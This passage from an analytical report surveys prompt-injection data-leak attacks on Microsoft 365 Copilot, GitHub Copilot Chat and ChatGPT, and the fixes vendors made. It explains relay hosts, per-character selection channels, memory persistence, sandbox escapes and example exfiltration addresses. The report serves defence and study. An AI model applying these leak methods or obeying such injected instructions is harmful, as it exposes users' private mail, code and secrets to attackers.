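The search page's Content Security Policy still blocked images from unknown hosts, so Varonis also needed a relay. The policy allowed every subdomain of `bing.com`, and Bing has a "Search by Image" feature that accepts the address of a picture and fetches it from Bing's servers for analysis. The user's browser contacted Bing, which then requested an address on the attacker's server that contained the stolen text.

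In the demonstration, that text was the title of an email. Email titles often contain the one-time codes that websites send to confirm a login. The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* points out that such a code may remain valid for several minutes, which is enough time for an attacker to use it. The attack could reach any mail, meetings and indexed files the victim was allowed to open.

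The Bing entry was already in the list of image hosts that Ravia had published a year earlier. EchoLeak had shown that a fetching service on a permitted host defeats the policy, so auditing the listed hosts for other such services could have found Bing's. Taler now recommends this audit to security teams.

### A dispute over severity

Microsoft published its record of SearchLeak, *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), on June 4 as CVE-2026-42824, and Varonis published its account on June 15. Microsoft rated the flaw critical on its own scale but gave it 6.5, or medium, on the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), a standard scale from 0 to 10.

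The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails* (2026) reported that the US government's National Vulnerability Database had scored the flaw 7.5. Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails* attributed the difference from Microsoft's score to one part of the scoring formula, which covers whether the attack requires the user to act. Microsoft had said it does, and the database had said it does not. The Next Web disputed that the scores differed, because it found 6.5 in both records. The database may have changed its entry between the two reports.

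The victim had to click a link, so a score of 6.5 follows the formula more closely. But the click only delivered the instructions, and sending the data out through Bing did not require it. An attacker who could deliver instructions without a click could therefore send data out by the same type of route, and Cato AI Labs did this within weeks.

### ReLeak: three more exits

Cato AI Labs, formerly Aim Labs, became part of the networking company Cato when it bought Aim Security in September 2025. The lab published its new findings on December 3 in *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026). All three attacks began, like EchoLeak, with an unread email that Copilot retrieved while answering an ordinary request. *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) reports that Microsoft's protections against prompt injection blocked none of them.

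In one attack, Copilot put private data into an image address, the user's browser loaded the image, and Bing passed the data to an outside server. *Письмо даже не нужно открывать* (Antipov, 2026) compares the attack with SearchLeak, which used a similar channel but needed a click. Microsoft fixed the flaw under CVE-2026-124115.

**A link inside a saved file.** Copilot can create Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF documents and save them in the user's storage. In this attack, the document contained a link with private data in its address. Microsoft's servers process stored files in the background, and they sent the data out when they processed this one. In Cato's tests, this happened one to eight minutes after the conversation ended, even if nobody opened the document. The flaw is CVE-2026-124132.

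None of the checks from 2025 applied to that file. The link was not in the displayed answer, so neither the code that cleans answers nor the browser's policy could catch it. A destination check on the tool call would have found only the company's own storage. To stop the leak, Microsoft would have to check addresses inside the documents that Copilot writes, or block its background software from contacting outside hosts. Blocking would also cover files from other sources, but it could break documents that legitimately load outside material.

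Copilot can write Python programs and run them in a sandbox, which is meant to isolate them from other systems. Microsoft says in its documentation that no network traffic enters or leaves the sandbox. Cato got around this restriction, and a program running there sent data directly to an outside server. Microsoft rated the flaw, CVE-2026-78501, as critical. Antipov reports that its CVSS score rose from 7.4 to 8.6.

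A ban on all traffic is the simplest destination check, the same as an allowlist with no entries. Here the rule was sound but its enforcement failed, unlike in the Bing attacks, where the browser correctly enforced a poor allowlist. Customers had little way to discover the failure themselves because Microsoft runs the sandbox. *AI sandbox escape uncovered in Microsoft Copilot flaw* (Knight, 2026) covers a similar weakness from separate research in August, which used a single Word document to break out of Copilot's sandbox into Microsoft's cloud.

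Agents built with two other Microsoft products, Agent Builder and Copilot Studio, can use the same code tool, but Antipov found no confirmation that the flaw affected them. Cato's researchers used AI agents to write test cases, study Copilot's refusals and adjust the next attempt. This automation makes it easier to search a large product for ways to send data out, and attackers can use it too.

Cato reported the three flaws between July 29 and August 20, 2026. Microsoft fixed the sandbox on September 17, the saved files on November 11 and the Bing route on November 15. Faisal reports that, according to Microsoft, customers don't need to do anything because the fixes are on Microsoft's servers. Cato knew of no real attacks or affected customers. AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) gives the same dates and also says Cato knew of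 no exploitation.

### Has there been too little progress?

A year after EchoLeak, Cato concluded that "too little progress has been made". Cato sells security products for AI systems and benefits when customers believe this, so the record of patches is a better guide to progress than its claim.

| Exit | Machine that contacted the attacker | Fixed |
|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak: Teams preview | Teams server | May 2025 |
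| SearchLeak: image search | Bing server | By June 2026 |
| ReLeak: code | Copilot's sandbox | September 17, 2026 |
| ReLeak: saved file | Microsoft's file-processing server | November 11, 2026 |
| ReLeak: image | Bing server | November 15, 2026 |

The strongest evidence for Cato's argument comes from Bing. Microsoft had fixed SearchLeak by mid-June, but Cato reported another leak through Bing that same summer, and that leak stayed open until November. The SearchLeak patch may have corrected the early image request but not the relay, or it may have closed one Bing address and left open another that could be used the same way. Either way, Microsoft fixed the attack that Varonis had demonstrated but not the general weakness, which EchoLeak had exposed in 2025.

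The other two ReLeak flaws support the verdict less well. They relied on Copilot's ability to save documents and run code, so no patch for displayed images could have fixed them. They do suggest that Microsoft released these abilities without testing every way they could send data out. The sandbox flaw is the more serious lapse because Microsoft had explicitly promised that this route did not exist.

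Cato also complains that the model still could not reliably separate a stranger's text from legitimate instructions. This is accurate, but it is a weak measure of Microsoft's effort because no developer has solved that problem. Microsoft has more control over the routes by which data can leave. It repaired the sandbox four to seven weeks after Cato's report, compared with roughly four months for EchoLeak and 12 to 16 weeks for the Bing route.

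### Closing a relay

In all five leaks, a machine run by Microsoft sent the last request. Microsoft can therefore check the request at that point, which most developers cannot do. But Bing and Teams cannot simply refuse to contact unfamiliar hosts, because people use image search and link previews for pages anywhere on the web.

The services could instead check how a request reached them. Modern browsers label each request to show whether it is for a whole page or for an image to insert into one. Bing's image search normally opens as a page, so it could refuse requests to load it as an image on another site. The preview service in Teams could require proof that a person posted the link in a chat. These checks would keep the normal features working but stop an assistant's answer from triggering them.

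Microsoft could also move the pictures Copilot needs to a host that only stores files and remove Bing, Teams and SharePoint from the image policy. Copilot would then be unable to show pictures directly from those services, and somebody would have to copy the useful ones to the new host.

Reddy and Gujral suggest cleaning the query strings of permitted addresses. The SharePoint, Teams and Bing relays in EchoLeak and SearchLeak all received the attacker's address in the query string, so removing the query string would have disabled all three. The display code would have to do this because a Content Security Policy cannot. But many legitimate images would stop loading, because websites also use the query string for an image's size or for a temporary key that proves the viewer may see the image.

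## GitHub Copilot Chat: an image proxy with signed addresses

GitHub, Microsoft's code-hosting site, fetches outside images through a proxy called Camo. Unlike Bing's image search, Camo refuses any address without GitHub's signature. A language model cannot forge the signature, so it cannot write private data into a new address and have Camo fetch it. In 2025 a researcher still leaked private code through Camo, using only addresses that GitHub had signed in advance.

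### How Camo signs an address

GitHub built Camo to prevent browser warnings, not to stop data theft. Users put pictures from other sites in their comments and project pages, and browsers displayed warnings when an encrypted page contained an unencrypted picture. GitHub's *Sidejack Prevention Phase 3* describes rewriting the image addresses to avoid these warnings. GitHub later rewrote the addresses of encrypted pictures too, so that outside sites would not receive details of each reader's browser, according to GitHub's *Proxying User Images*.

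The process has four steps:

1. A user saves a comment containing a picture from `pictures.example/cats/logo.png`.
2. GitHub's code computes a signature from that address and a secret key. It then replaces the address with `camo.githubusercontent.com/SIGNATURE/ADDRESS`, where the last part is the original address in encoded form.
3. A reader's browser requests the new address from Camo.
4. Camo decodes the original address and computes the signature again. It fetches the picture only if the two signatures match.

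The signature is a hash-based message authentication code (HMAC). Any change to the address requires a different signature, and only someone with the key can compute it. If a model adds `?w=marmalade` to the original address, the old signature no longer matches, so Camo doesn't fetch the image.

### Why the signature looked sufficient

GitHub already used a Content Security Policy to limit which hosts its pages could load images from (GitHub, 2016). The security firm Cure53 then found that some of the allowed hosts could pass data on to an attacker (GitHub, 2017). Google Analytics would record arbitrary text for any account holder, and the profile-picture service Gravatar would fetch a substitute picture from an address in the query string. GitHub removed both from the list of allowed hosts and began loading Gravatar pictures through its image proxy, Camo.

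GitHub reasoned that an attacker could inject a working Camo address only if they knew the entire address beforehand. In the attacks GitHub was considering, the attacker left an image tag unfinished, and the browser treated the text that followed as part of the address. That text was the secret, so the attacker could not get an address containing it signed in advance. The argument holds for a fixed piece of HTML, but it does not cover a model that reads the secret first and then chooses among signed addresses.

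In 2024, Copilot Chat, GitHub's assistant for questions about code, had an ordinary image leak in its extension for the VS Code editor. Instructions in a source file could lead the assistant to put earlier chat messages into an image address. Rehberger reported the flaw on February 25 and received confirmation of a fix on June 12. According to Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat*, the extension apparently stopped displaying Markdown images, but Willison's *GitHub Copilot Chat* describes the fix as blocking images from untrusted domains.

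On GitHub's website, the same attack would have failed because the browser would have blocked the attacker's host and Camo would have rejected an unsigned address. This seemed to solve the problem of trusted relays without blocking external images.

### CamoLeak: one signed address per character

Omer Mayraz of Legit Security found a way around both checks in June 2025. His attack, described in Legit Security's *CamoLeak*, began with a pull request, which is a proposed change to a project's code. GitHub lets authors include comments that the page does not display, and Mayraz put instructions in one. The project's owner received the usual notification, without the hidden text. When any user asked Copilot Chat about the pull request, the model also read the instructions, and it had access to that user's private code.

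Mayraz first had Copilot write a link containing private data, but the user had to click it. To make the leak automatic, Mayraz needed images that Camo would accept. Getting addresses signed was easy because GitHub offers a programming interface that converts Markdown and returns it with signed image addresses. According to GitHub's documentation, anyone who receives such an address can view the picture, so GitHub does not tie the address to one page or user. The signature proves that GitHub's software processed the address, but does not identify who owns the server behind it. GitHub explains in Camo's notes that signing lets it clear stored copies and ban or limit requests.

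Mayraz obtained a signed address for each letter and symbol, all pointing to Mayraz's server, and put the list in the hidden instructions. To leak "marmalade", the model would insert nine images, one for each letter in order. The browser would request them from Camo, which would fetch them from the server, and the order of the requests would spell the word. The server returned a transparent one-pixel image each time, so the images were invisible in the chat.

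Browsers keep copies of pictures they have already loaded, so a repeated letter, such as the second m, would produce no new request, and the log would read "marlde". Mayraz therefore had the model add a new random number to the end of each Camo address. The browser then treated each picture as new, and Camo still accepted the request because the signature covers only the original address.

In the demonstrations, Copilot leaked the description of an undisclosed security flaw from a private project. It also searched a victim's code for cloud access keys and sent out the result.

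This is a selection channel, a leak that conveys information through the choice among permitted addresses. Each address was valid and contained nothing secret, so a content filter checking them one at a time would have found nothing to block. The same weakness affects the rules that ChatGPT may load only addresses already public on the web and that Claude's web fetch tool may open only addresses already in the conversation.

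### Severity and fix

Legit Security gives CamoLeak a CVSS score of 9.6, slightly above EchoLeak's. VPN Central's *Hackers exploited GitHub Copilot flaw to exfiltrate sensitive data from private repositories* mistakenly lists it as CVE-2025-59145. The official record for that identifier, MITRE's *color-name@2.0.1 contains malware after npm account takeover* (2025), describes malicious code in a software package.

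SecurityWeek's *GitHub Copilot Chat Flaw Leaked Data From Private Repositories* reports that GitHub told Mayraz on August 14, 2025, that it had fixed the problem by disallowing the use of Camo to leak user data. Legit Security says more specifically that GitHub turned off images in Copilot Chat completely. Press coverage listed in OECD's *GitHub Copilot Chat Vulnerability Exposes Private Code and Secrets* (2025) dates from October 8, almost two months after the fix.

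Without images, the chat sends no automatic image requests that a model could use to leak data. Users lose diagrams and screenshots in answers, and removing images does not by itself stop leaks through clicked links. Under its bug bounty rules, GitHub pays nothing for showing that hidden text can influence Copilot, but may pay if the result is a concrete harm such as exposing data from another repository.

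### How much a choice can carry

Information theory gives a limit on what a selection channel can leak. With *b* bits, one can distinguish 2 to the power *b* possibilities. If a model can request one of *N* addresses, the attacker can distinguish at most *N* outcomes, so the request carries at most log₂ *N* bits. This is 5 bits for 32 addresses and about 5.17 for 36.

Suppose the secret is a random eight-character code made from 26 letters and ten digits. There are 36⁸, or about 2.8 trillion, possible codes, which is 41.4 bits of information. With 36 addresses, one for each letter and digit, the model needs eight requests to send the code. With 1,000 addresses, it needs five, because four requests allow only one trillion different sequences.

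These figures are upper bounds. They assume that the attacker and the model share the list, that the model makes no mistakes, and that every request reaches the attacker in order. They also assume a fixed number of requests and exclude any information carried by their timing. If the model may stop early, the number of requests also carries information, but this adds less than half a bit to the totals here. Sending or not sending already conveys a bit, as Metere (2026) points out in *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress*, so a limit of zero is unrealistic as long as the model decides whether to send anything.

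### Banning repeat visits

Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* suggests that an agent should not visit the same full address twice in a session, or should reuse a stored copy for a few minutes. To work against CamoLeak, the rule would have to ignore the random number at the end of each address, because otherwise every address would count as new.

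With 36 addresses and no repeats, the model has 36 choices for its first request, 35 for its second, and so on down to 29 for its eighth. Multiplying these eight numbers gives 1.22 trillion possible sequences, or 40.2 bits. Banning repeats removes only 1.2 bits. The ban would still disrupt a simple scheme with one address per character, because only 43% of random eight-character codes have no repeated characters. A more elaborate encoding could use nearly all of the remaining capacity.

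The ban is more effective if the attacker cannot see the order in which the addresses are requested. Eight different addresses can arrive in 40,320 orders, which the attacker can no longer tell apart. Dividing 1.22 trillion by 40,320 leaves 30.3 million sets, or 24.9 bits. On average, about 93,000 codes would then remain possible. That is too many to try on a login page that locks after a few failures, but a computer that can test guesses without a limit could try them all quickly.

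| What the attacker can use | 8 requests, 36 addresses | 5 requests, 1,000 addresses |
|---|---:|---:|
| Order visible, repeats allowed | 41.4 bits | 49.8 bits |
| Order visible, no repeats | 40.2 bits | 49.8 bits |
| Order hidden, repeats allowed | 27.1 bits | 42.9 bits |
| Order hidden, no repeats | 24.9 bits | 42.9 bits |

Hiding the order therefore matters much more than banning repeats. With 1,000 addresses, even both measures together don't protect the code, because five different addresses in any order still provide 42.9 bits, more than the 41.4 needed. Embrace The Red notes that an attacker could use thousands of addresses. With Camo, the main obstacle would be space in the injected text, since each signed address is more than 100 characters long and 1,000 of them would take over 100,000 characters.

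A ban on repeat requests also limits how much data can leave in one session, because the model runs out of addresses after 36 requests. The order of those requests can carry at most 138 bits. A random forty-character key made from the same symbols holds 207 bits, so the model could not send the whole key. A longer list of addresses or a second session would remove that protection.

### Errors in practice

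Real selection channels can fall well short of these limits. *Actions Speak Louder than Words* (Liang, Deng and colleagues, 2026) tests a version in which nobody tells the agent to send data. A link on an ordinary page leads a research agent to the attacker's site, which offers references on different topics. The agent opens the one that best fits its task, and this choice reveals something about the user's question. The attacker can then offer narrower topics and repeat the process.

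With four references, the attacker identified the right topic in 93.8% of the trials that produced a signal. When the order of requests carried the information instead, accuracy fell to 67.9%, partly because agents reorder requests or send several at once. Adding references also increased errors, and with sixteen the attacker was right half the time. If the wrong answers were spread evenly, sixteen references leaked less information than four, about 1 bit of a possible 4 compared with about 1.6 of a possible 2. CamoLeak probably had fewer such errors because its list assigned one address to each character, so the model did not have to judge which topic was relevant.

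Despite errors, repeated choices let the attack recover the concepts in users' questions with an average F1 score of 0.89 across four agents and three models. A score of 1 means that the attack found every concept and added no false ones. Four existing defences, including a filter on tool inputs and outputs, lowered the scores by no more than 0.03.

### Limiting the choice

Metere proposes a budget of leaked bits for each destination. The budget refills over time, and when it runs out, the monitor delays or blocks further suspicious messages. Metere's scanner estimates the leak from features such as long encoded strings, so it would not measure the information leaked by choosing between two valid addresses. A rule for images could instead deduct log₂ *N* bits per request, where *N* is the number of addresses the attacker has supplied. With 36 addresses, each request would use 5.17 bits, so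 a budget of 20 bits would permit three images. This rule would be difficult to apply because the code doesn't know *N*.

Metere's monitor also puts batches of outgoing images into a fixed order. A chat application could do something similar by waiting for the complete answer and then requesting its images one at a time, in alphabetical order of address. This would reduce what the eight-image example can leak from 41.4 to 27.1 bits, but users would have to wait for the images.

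Liang and colleagues try to make the requests entirely independent of the private data. Their defence fetches a fixed number of pages without using the private context, and the agent then chooses among the stored copies, where the attacker cannot observe the choice. This lowered the F1 score from 0.89 to 0.39. In Copilot Chat, the equivalent would be to load every image in a pull request before the model reads any private code, and to show only those copies in the answer. Turning images off achieves the same independence more simply, because Copilot Chat then makes no image requests, regardless of the secret.

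## ChatGPT: loading only addresses already public on the web

ChatGPT may load a web address automatically only if that exact address is already public. OpenAI keeps a list of such addresses using a crawler, a program that follows links and records the addresses it finds. An address containing a user's secret will almost never be on the list, because nobody has published it. OpenAI described this rule in January 2026, after researchers had repeatedly bypassed its earlier check, url_safe, by sending data through hosts that url_safe allowed.

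### url_safe and its undisclosed rule

The first version of url_safe appeared in ChatGPT's web app in December 2023. Before the app displayed an image, it sent the image's address to OpenAI's servers, which replied whether it was safe. The same check covered ordinary links, according to Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025).

OpenAI did not say how its servers checked addresses. Rehberger guessed that they might look them up in Bing's index. Commenting on Embrace The Red's report, Willison called the change a "half-baked solution" and expected attackers to get data past the check in file names or subdomains. The iOS app did not have the check yet, and Embrace The Red later reported that the macOS app lacked it too.

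In October 2024 Rehberger reported several addresses that url_safe wrongly accepted. One was on `windows.net`, where Microsoft's cloud customers can open storage accounts and read a log of every request to them. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* shows how an attacker could use such an account. ChatGPT keeps a record of the user's recent conversations in the model's context, and hidden instructions in a PDF led it to copy this record into an image address on Rehberger's storage account. A document opened in one chat could therefore leak what the user had written in others.

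Tenable found another gap that December. The check always accepted `bing.com`, and Bing's search results use `bing.com` links that forward visitors to the real site. So anyone whose site appeared in Bing's results had a trusted address that led to it.

Both gaps were still open when the researchers published them in 2025. Rehberger had asked OpenAI to publish the list of safe domains and let business customers edit it. Customers could then have removed `windows.net` themselves. Publishing the list would have helped attackers look for gaps, but they were finding them anyway. Rehberger says that OpenAI next tightened the restrictions in about August 2025 and that this stopped the attacks demonstrated up to then.

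### ZombieAgent

After an attack called ShadowLeak, OpenAI also barred ChatGPT from adding anything to an address found in outside content, so ChatGPT could open the address only exactly as written. Anthropic uses a similar rule for Claude's web fetch tool.

The security company Radware bypassed this by supplying ready-made addresses. In Radware's *ZombieAgent*, the attacker sends an email containing one address for each letter and digit, plus one for a space. When the user later asks ChatGPT to do something in Gmail, ChatGPT reads the email and opens the addresses whose characters spell out the private data. The requests come from OpenAI's servers before the user sees an answer, so no protection in the browser can stop them.

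CamoLeak had used this selection channel in GitHub's Copilot Chat a few months earlier. Radware improved on it by making a separate address for each character in each position. An address ending in `a0` meant the first character was an "a", and `a1` meant the second one was. An eight-character code made from letters and digits needs 288 addresses. The attacker can then reconstruct the code even if the requests arrive out of order, and the model never has to open the same address twice.

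Radware also made the leak permanent by using Memory, a feature in which ChatGPT saves notes about the user. OpenAI had tried to keep Memory apart from connected services such as Gmail by blocking it in a chat once ChatGPT had used one of those services there. But ChatGPT could still use Memory first and the connected service afterwards. A shared file could therefore plant a note telling ChatGPT to open the attacker's email every time the user sent a message and follow the instructions in it. A second note told ChatGPT to save any sensitive information the user mentioned.

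Radware reported the flaw on September 26, 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on December 16. According to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, a news article from January 2026, ChatGPT now opens a link from an email only if the link is in a public index or the user provided it. The article says the attack worked because OpenAI had not stopped ChatGPT from adding a single letter to an address. Radware, which is more likely to be right because it built the attack, says the email contained every address in full, so a ban on adding letters would not have stopped the attack.

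It is not entirely clear when the index rule began. Rehberger connects it with the August tightening, but ZombieAgent still worked in September. The rule probably did not cover links in emails until the December fix.

### Comparing each address with an index

Adrian Spânu and Thomas Shadwell explained the new rule for OpenAI on January 28, 2026, in an article and a technical paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. It works as follows:

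1. The crawler scans public web pages and records their addresses, much as a search engine does. It has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data.
2. When ChatGPT is about to load a page or an image, code compares the full address with the crawler's index.
3. If the address is in the index, ChatGPT loads it without asking.
4. If it is not, the code either tells the model to try a different website or shows the user a warning before anything opens.

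The rule works only if the crawler finds addresses independently of users' conversations. If the index also recorded addresses that ChatGPT had opened, an address containing "marmalade" would count as public after ChatGPT opened it once, perhaps because a user clicked past a warning.

OpenAI's rule would have stopped most of the leaks in the products covered so far. Superhuman trusted `docs.google.com`, so an attacker's Google Form on that host could collect emails. The rule would have blocked this because the address that fills in the form with someone's mail would not be in the index, though the blank form's address might be. It would also have stopped the Bing and Teams relays in Microsoft 365 Copilot and the attack using Rehberger's storage account, since each needed a new address containing the stolen text.

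Besides the problem of redirects, OpenAI avoided relying on a short list of reputable sites because people visit far more than a handful of well-known sites, so they would see constant warnings. The index covers far more sites, though it is stricter about which addresses within a site it allows. A page on a hobbyist's blog passes as easily as one on a national newspaper's site, provided that the crawler has found it.

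Some harmless addresses will still fail the check. A page published an hour ago may not be in the index yet, and the crawler can't reach pages behind a login. Addresses that a site creates for one person, such as a link for tracking a parcel, should not be in the index. These addresses can contain the kind of personal data the rule is meant to protect, so a warning is reasonable even when the user wants the page.

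### Redirects, typed addresses and the warning

A redirect often takes its destination from the query string. An attacker could use one on a respectable site like this:

`trusted.example/go?to=collector.example/marmalade`

A rule that checks only the first host accepts this address, and the site then forwards the request to the attacker. The index rule rejects the address because nobody has published it with "marmalade" at the end.

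The index may still contain redirects that lead to an attacker's server. These are much less useful to the attacker because the address was fixed before the conversation began. The attacker can later change where the redirect leads, but can't include the secret in the new address because neither server has received it. The attacker learns only that someone opened the link.

As Embrace The Red understands it, ChatGPT makes an exception for addresses in the user's own messages, treating them as safe for the rest of that chat even if they are not in the index. This provenance rule lets people ask about private or very new pages without a warning, but it relies on users knowing what they have put in their messages. In Samoilenko's 2023 attack, a rigged web page added hidden text to whatever the user copied from it. If ChatGPT treats pasted addresses like typed ones, the hidden text could include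 one address for each letter, and all of them would count as safe.

When ChatGPT cannot verify a link, it may show a box titled "Check this link is safe". The box contains a warning that the link might share conversation data with another site, the link's address, and options to copy or open it. OpenAI advises users who notice anything odd not to open the link and to ask for another source.

Showing the user the address helps if the stolen word is readable in it, as in `?w=marmalade`, but helps less if the word is encoded, because many ordinary addresses also contain long strings of random-looking characters. In an attack like ZombieAgent, the addresses differ by only one or two characters, and none contains anything suspicious. The number of warnings might alert the user, but by then the attacker could already have the first few letters.

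### Safe Url

In March 2026 OpenAI called this protection Safe Url and referred readers to the January article and paper for details. It described Safe Url as a way to detect when information from a conversation is about to go to a third party. Safe Url treats any address that is not in the index of public addresses as one that might contain private information, so it doesn't have to recognize private information as a content filter would.

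OpenAI says that most attacks on ChatGPT fail before Safe Url is needed, because the model refuses to send the data. Safe Url is for cases in which the model is persuaded. The article describes a 2025 email that looked like a follow-up to a meeting about restructuring. It told the assistant to find an employee's name and address and submit them to a "compliance validation system". The attack succeeded in half of the tests when the user asked for deep research on the day's emails. OpenAI says that injection detectors usually miss such emails, because recognizing them is as hard as recognizing a lie.

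The protection also applies outside the main chat:

- In Atlas, OpenAI's web browser, it covers pages that the agent opens and bookmarks that it creates. A bookmark sends nothing when the agent saves it, but it sends its whole address when the user opens it later.
- In Deep Research, which writes long reports from many sources, it covers searches as well as page visits.
- Canvas and ChatGPT Apps, which can run small programs inside ChatGPT, have a similar protection. The programs run in a sandbox that detects unexpected communication and asks the user for consent.

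### What the guarantee covers

OpenAI says the safeguards are meant to stop ChatGPT from "quietly leaking user-specific data through the URL itself" when it loads pages or images. It also says they do not make a page's content trustworthy or prevent a site from deceiving the user.

"Quietly" excludes leaks that the user approves in a warning box, and "through the URL itself" excludes data that leaves in another part of a request. For example, a browser agent could open a public page whose address is in the index and type "marmalade" into the page's comment form. The word would usually leave in the request body, and the address would contain nothing private.

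Other checks have to cover such actions. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) says that Atlas is designed to ask the user before it takes certain consequential steps, such as buying something or sending an email. OpenAI trained a model to search for attacks on Atlas, and one attack it found made the agent send a resignation letter to the user's boss when the user had asked for an out-of-office reply. A rule about web addresses would not stop that attack, because the harm was in a message to a familiar recipient.

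The promise also does not cover links that mislead the reader. eWeek's *‘ChatGPhish’ Attack Turns ChatGPT Summaries Into Phishing Lures* describes web pages that could put fake warnings, phishing links and malicious QR codes into ChatGPT's summaries of them. A phishing link does not need to contain private data, because its purpose is to get the user to type a password on the page it opens.

### Choosing among public addresses

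This protection is weakest against selection channels, which leak data through the choice of which public page to load. An attacker can publish a page for each letter and digit, wait for the crawler to index them, and then have the assistant load the pages that spell out the stolen data, as ZombieAgent did. Each request matches the index exactly. Embrace The Red notes that OpenAI's paper acknowledges this trick, which Rehberger first described in 2023. It adds that anyone with a fairly large blog probably already has the 36 indexed pages needed. With 10,000 indexed pages, one for each possible four-digit PIN, an attacker could learn a PIN from a single request.

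The index does make the attack slower and harder. Radware could invent new addresses and email them the same day. Under the index rule, the attacker has to publish the pages in advance and cannot be sure the crawler will record them all. OpenAI controls the index, so it could leave out sites with hundreds of nearly identical pages, though the attacker could respond by writing ordinary-looking articles.

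Rehberger's proposals to reuse stored copies or refuse repeat visits would not stop Radware's version, because it uses each address at most once. The attacker would need 288 indexed pages instead of 36 for an eight-character code, still a modest number for a website.

The ChatGPT product seems much harder to attack than a bare model. *The Framing Gap* (2026) recorded no leaks in 48 valid trials on the product, but the model leaked in up to 100% of trials when accessed through OpenAI's programming interface. The researchers could not observe the product's internal checks and did not attribute the difference to any of them, so the index rule may have contributed a lot or nothing. With only 48 trials, the product's true leak rate could be as high as about 6%.

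### Features without the check

Rehberger's last concern was that some developers at OpenAI might not know about the protection and would build features without it. One such feature was already leaking data when OpenAI published the rule.

Companies that build assistants on OpenAI's models can read past conversations in a log viewer on OpenAI's website. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* found that the viewer displayed images from any address. PromptArmor tested this with a mock assistant for bank employees who check customers' identities. The assistant combined a customer's passport and financial details with material from the web, some of which contained an injection. The model then wrote an image address containing the customer's data. The bank's application detected the problem and blocked the answer, so nothing leaked at that point.

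The application also flagged the conversation for review. When a developer opened the log, the viewer loaded the image and sent the customer's data to the attacker. The assistant's protection had worked, but it made a leak through the viewer more likely by drawing a developer's attention to the conversation. A user's complaint could do the same. If an application removes the image and leaves an odd, nearly empty answer, the user may click "thumbs down", and a developer may then look at the log.

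PromptArmor found the same flaw in several of OpenAI's tools for building and testing assistants, including the preview screens for new agents. It reported the problem on November 17, 2025. The company that handles OpenAI's bug reports closed the case as "not applicable" on December 4, and OpenAI learned of the report only after PromptArmor published its findings. On January 22, 2026, six days before announcing the index rule, OpenAI reopened the report and said it was working on a fix.

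The pattern continued with the Codex leak through a Google Form, which PromptArmor reported almost three months after the announcement. The index rule, which allows only addresses already public on the web, would have blocked the image address used in that leak.

Programs that ChatGPT runs can also send data without using its page-fetching tool. ChatGPT can write Python code and run it in a sandbox, where OpenAI restricts direct internet connections. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT data leakage via a hidden outbound channel* describes a way around this restriction that OpenAI had overlooked. A single malicious prompt in an ordinary conversation could make ChatGPT send a summary of the user's messages to an outside server without warning. Custom versions of ChatGPT, which anyone can make and share, could collect data from their users the same way. According to The Hacker News (2026), OpenAI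 fixed the flaw on February 20, 2026, and there was no evidence that attackers had used it.

### Lockdown Mode

For people who want stronger protection, OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode on February 13, 2026. It was first available to organizations such as companies, schools and healthcare providers, and OpenAI began offering it to personal accounts on June 4. The setting turns off features that could send data out, or limits them. In early December 2026, OpenAI's help page listed these effects:

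| Feature | In Lockdown Mode |
|---|---|
| Web browsing | Stored copies of pages only |
| Images from the web | ChatGPT may not show or retrieve them |
| Deep research and agent mode | Off |
| Programs in Canvas | No network access, even with the user's approval |
| Downloading files for analysis | Off |
| Uploading files, generating images, Memory | No change |
| Codex | No change to network access |

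Browsing only stored copies protects against more than the index rule does, because it also removes the selection channel from browsing. Under the index rule, ChatGPT still loads public pages from the attacker's server, so the attacker can see which pages it chose. In Lockdown Mode, ChatGPT reads copies from OpenAI's own storage. An injection can still make it open the pages for "m", "a" and "r", but the attacker's server receives no requests. Search results may be old or missing, so the mode is a poor choice for checking train times or today's news.

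OpenAI designed the setting for a small group, such as executives and security teams at prominent organizations. Willison infers that ChatGPT's default settings do not offer robust protection against a determined attacker. OpenAI's description of the index rule supports this reading, since OpenAI promises only that the rule stops data from leaving inside a web address.

### What can still leave in Lockdown Mode

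Connected apps are the largest remaining route for data to leave. On personal accounts, Lockdown Mode stops ChatGPT from accessing outside services live or making changes in them when this would conflict with the mode's protections. In organizations, administrators decide which apps and actions to allow, and Lockdown Mode does not automatically turn them all off.

OpenAI advises administrators to consider who could see the result of each action. If ChatGPT can post comments in a public project, a prompt injection can make it publish private data there, where the attacker can read it. OpenAI therefore recommends against letting an app write or change anything unless the administrator can confirm that an attacker would not see the result. It also advises against letting ChatGPT read from an untrusted app. The app's operator can see what ChatGPT looks up, so a lookup request can carry data out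 just as a web address can.

Users can turn Lockdown Mode off for a single chat, for example to load a live page, but Memory works whether the mode is on or off. If an uploaded file planted an instruction in Memory, as in ZombieAgent, that instruction could have no effect while the mode was on and then take effect in the chat where the user turned it off.

A flaw in another part of ChatGPT defeated the setting altogether. ChatGPT can show a working preview of a web page inside a chat. The preview runs in a sandbox that keeps the page from reading the user's ChatGPT data or contacting other sites without consent. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) explains how Check Point got around it:

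1. ChatGPT intercepted the preview's attempts to open new windows. But the sandbox's own permissions still allowed popup windows, and a popup did not have to follow the sandbox's rules.
2. The previewed page created another frame, which is a page within the page. The new frame had its own copy of the browser's function for opening windows, and ChatGPT had not modified that copy.
3. The page used this copy to open a popup, which could send the chat to the attacker's server.

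In the desktop app, the attack needed no click. The hostile page could come from a crafted prompt, a custom version of ChatGPT or a shared chat. OpenAI fixed the flaw on September 18, 2026, and Check Point published its findings on November 5. It would have been simpler to deny popups in the sandbox's permissions. The browser would then have refused to open the window, whichever copy of the function the page used.

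## Claude's web fetch tool: opening only addresses already in the conversation

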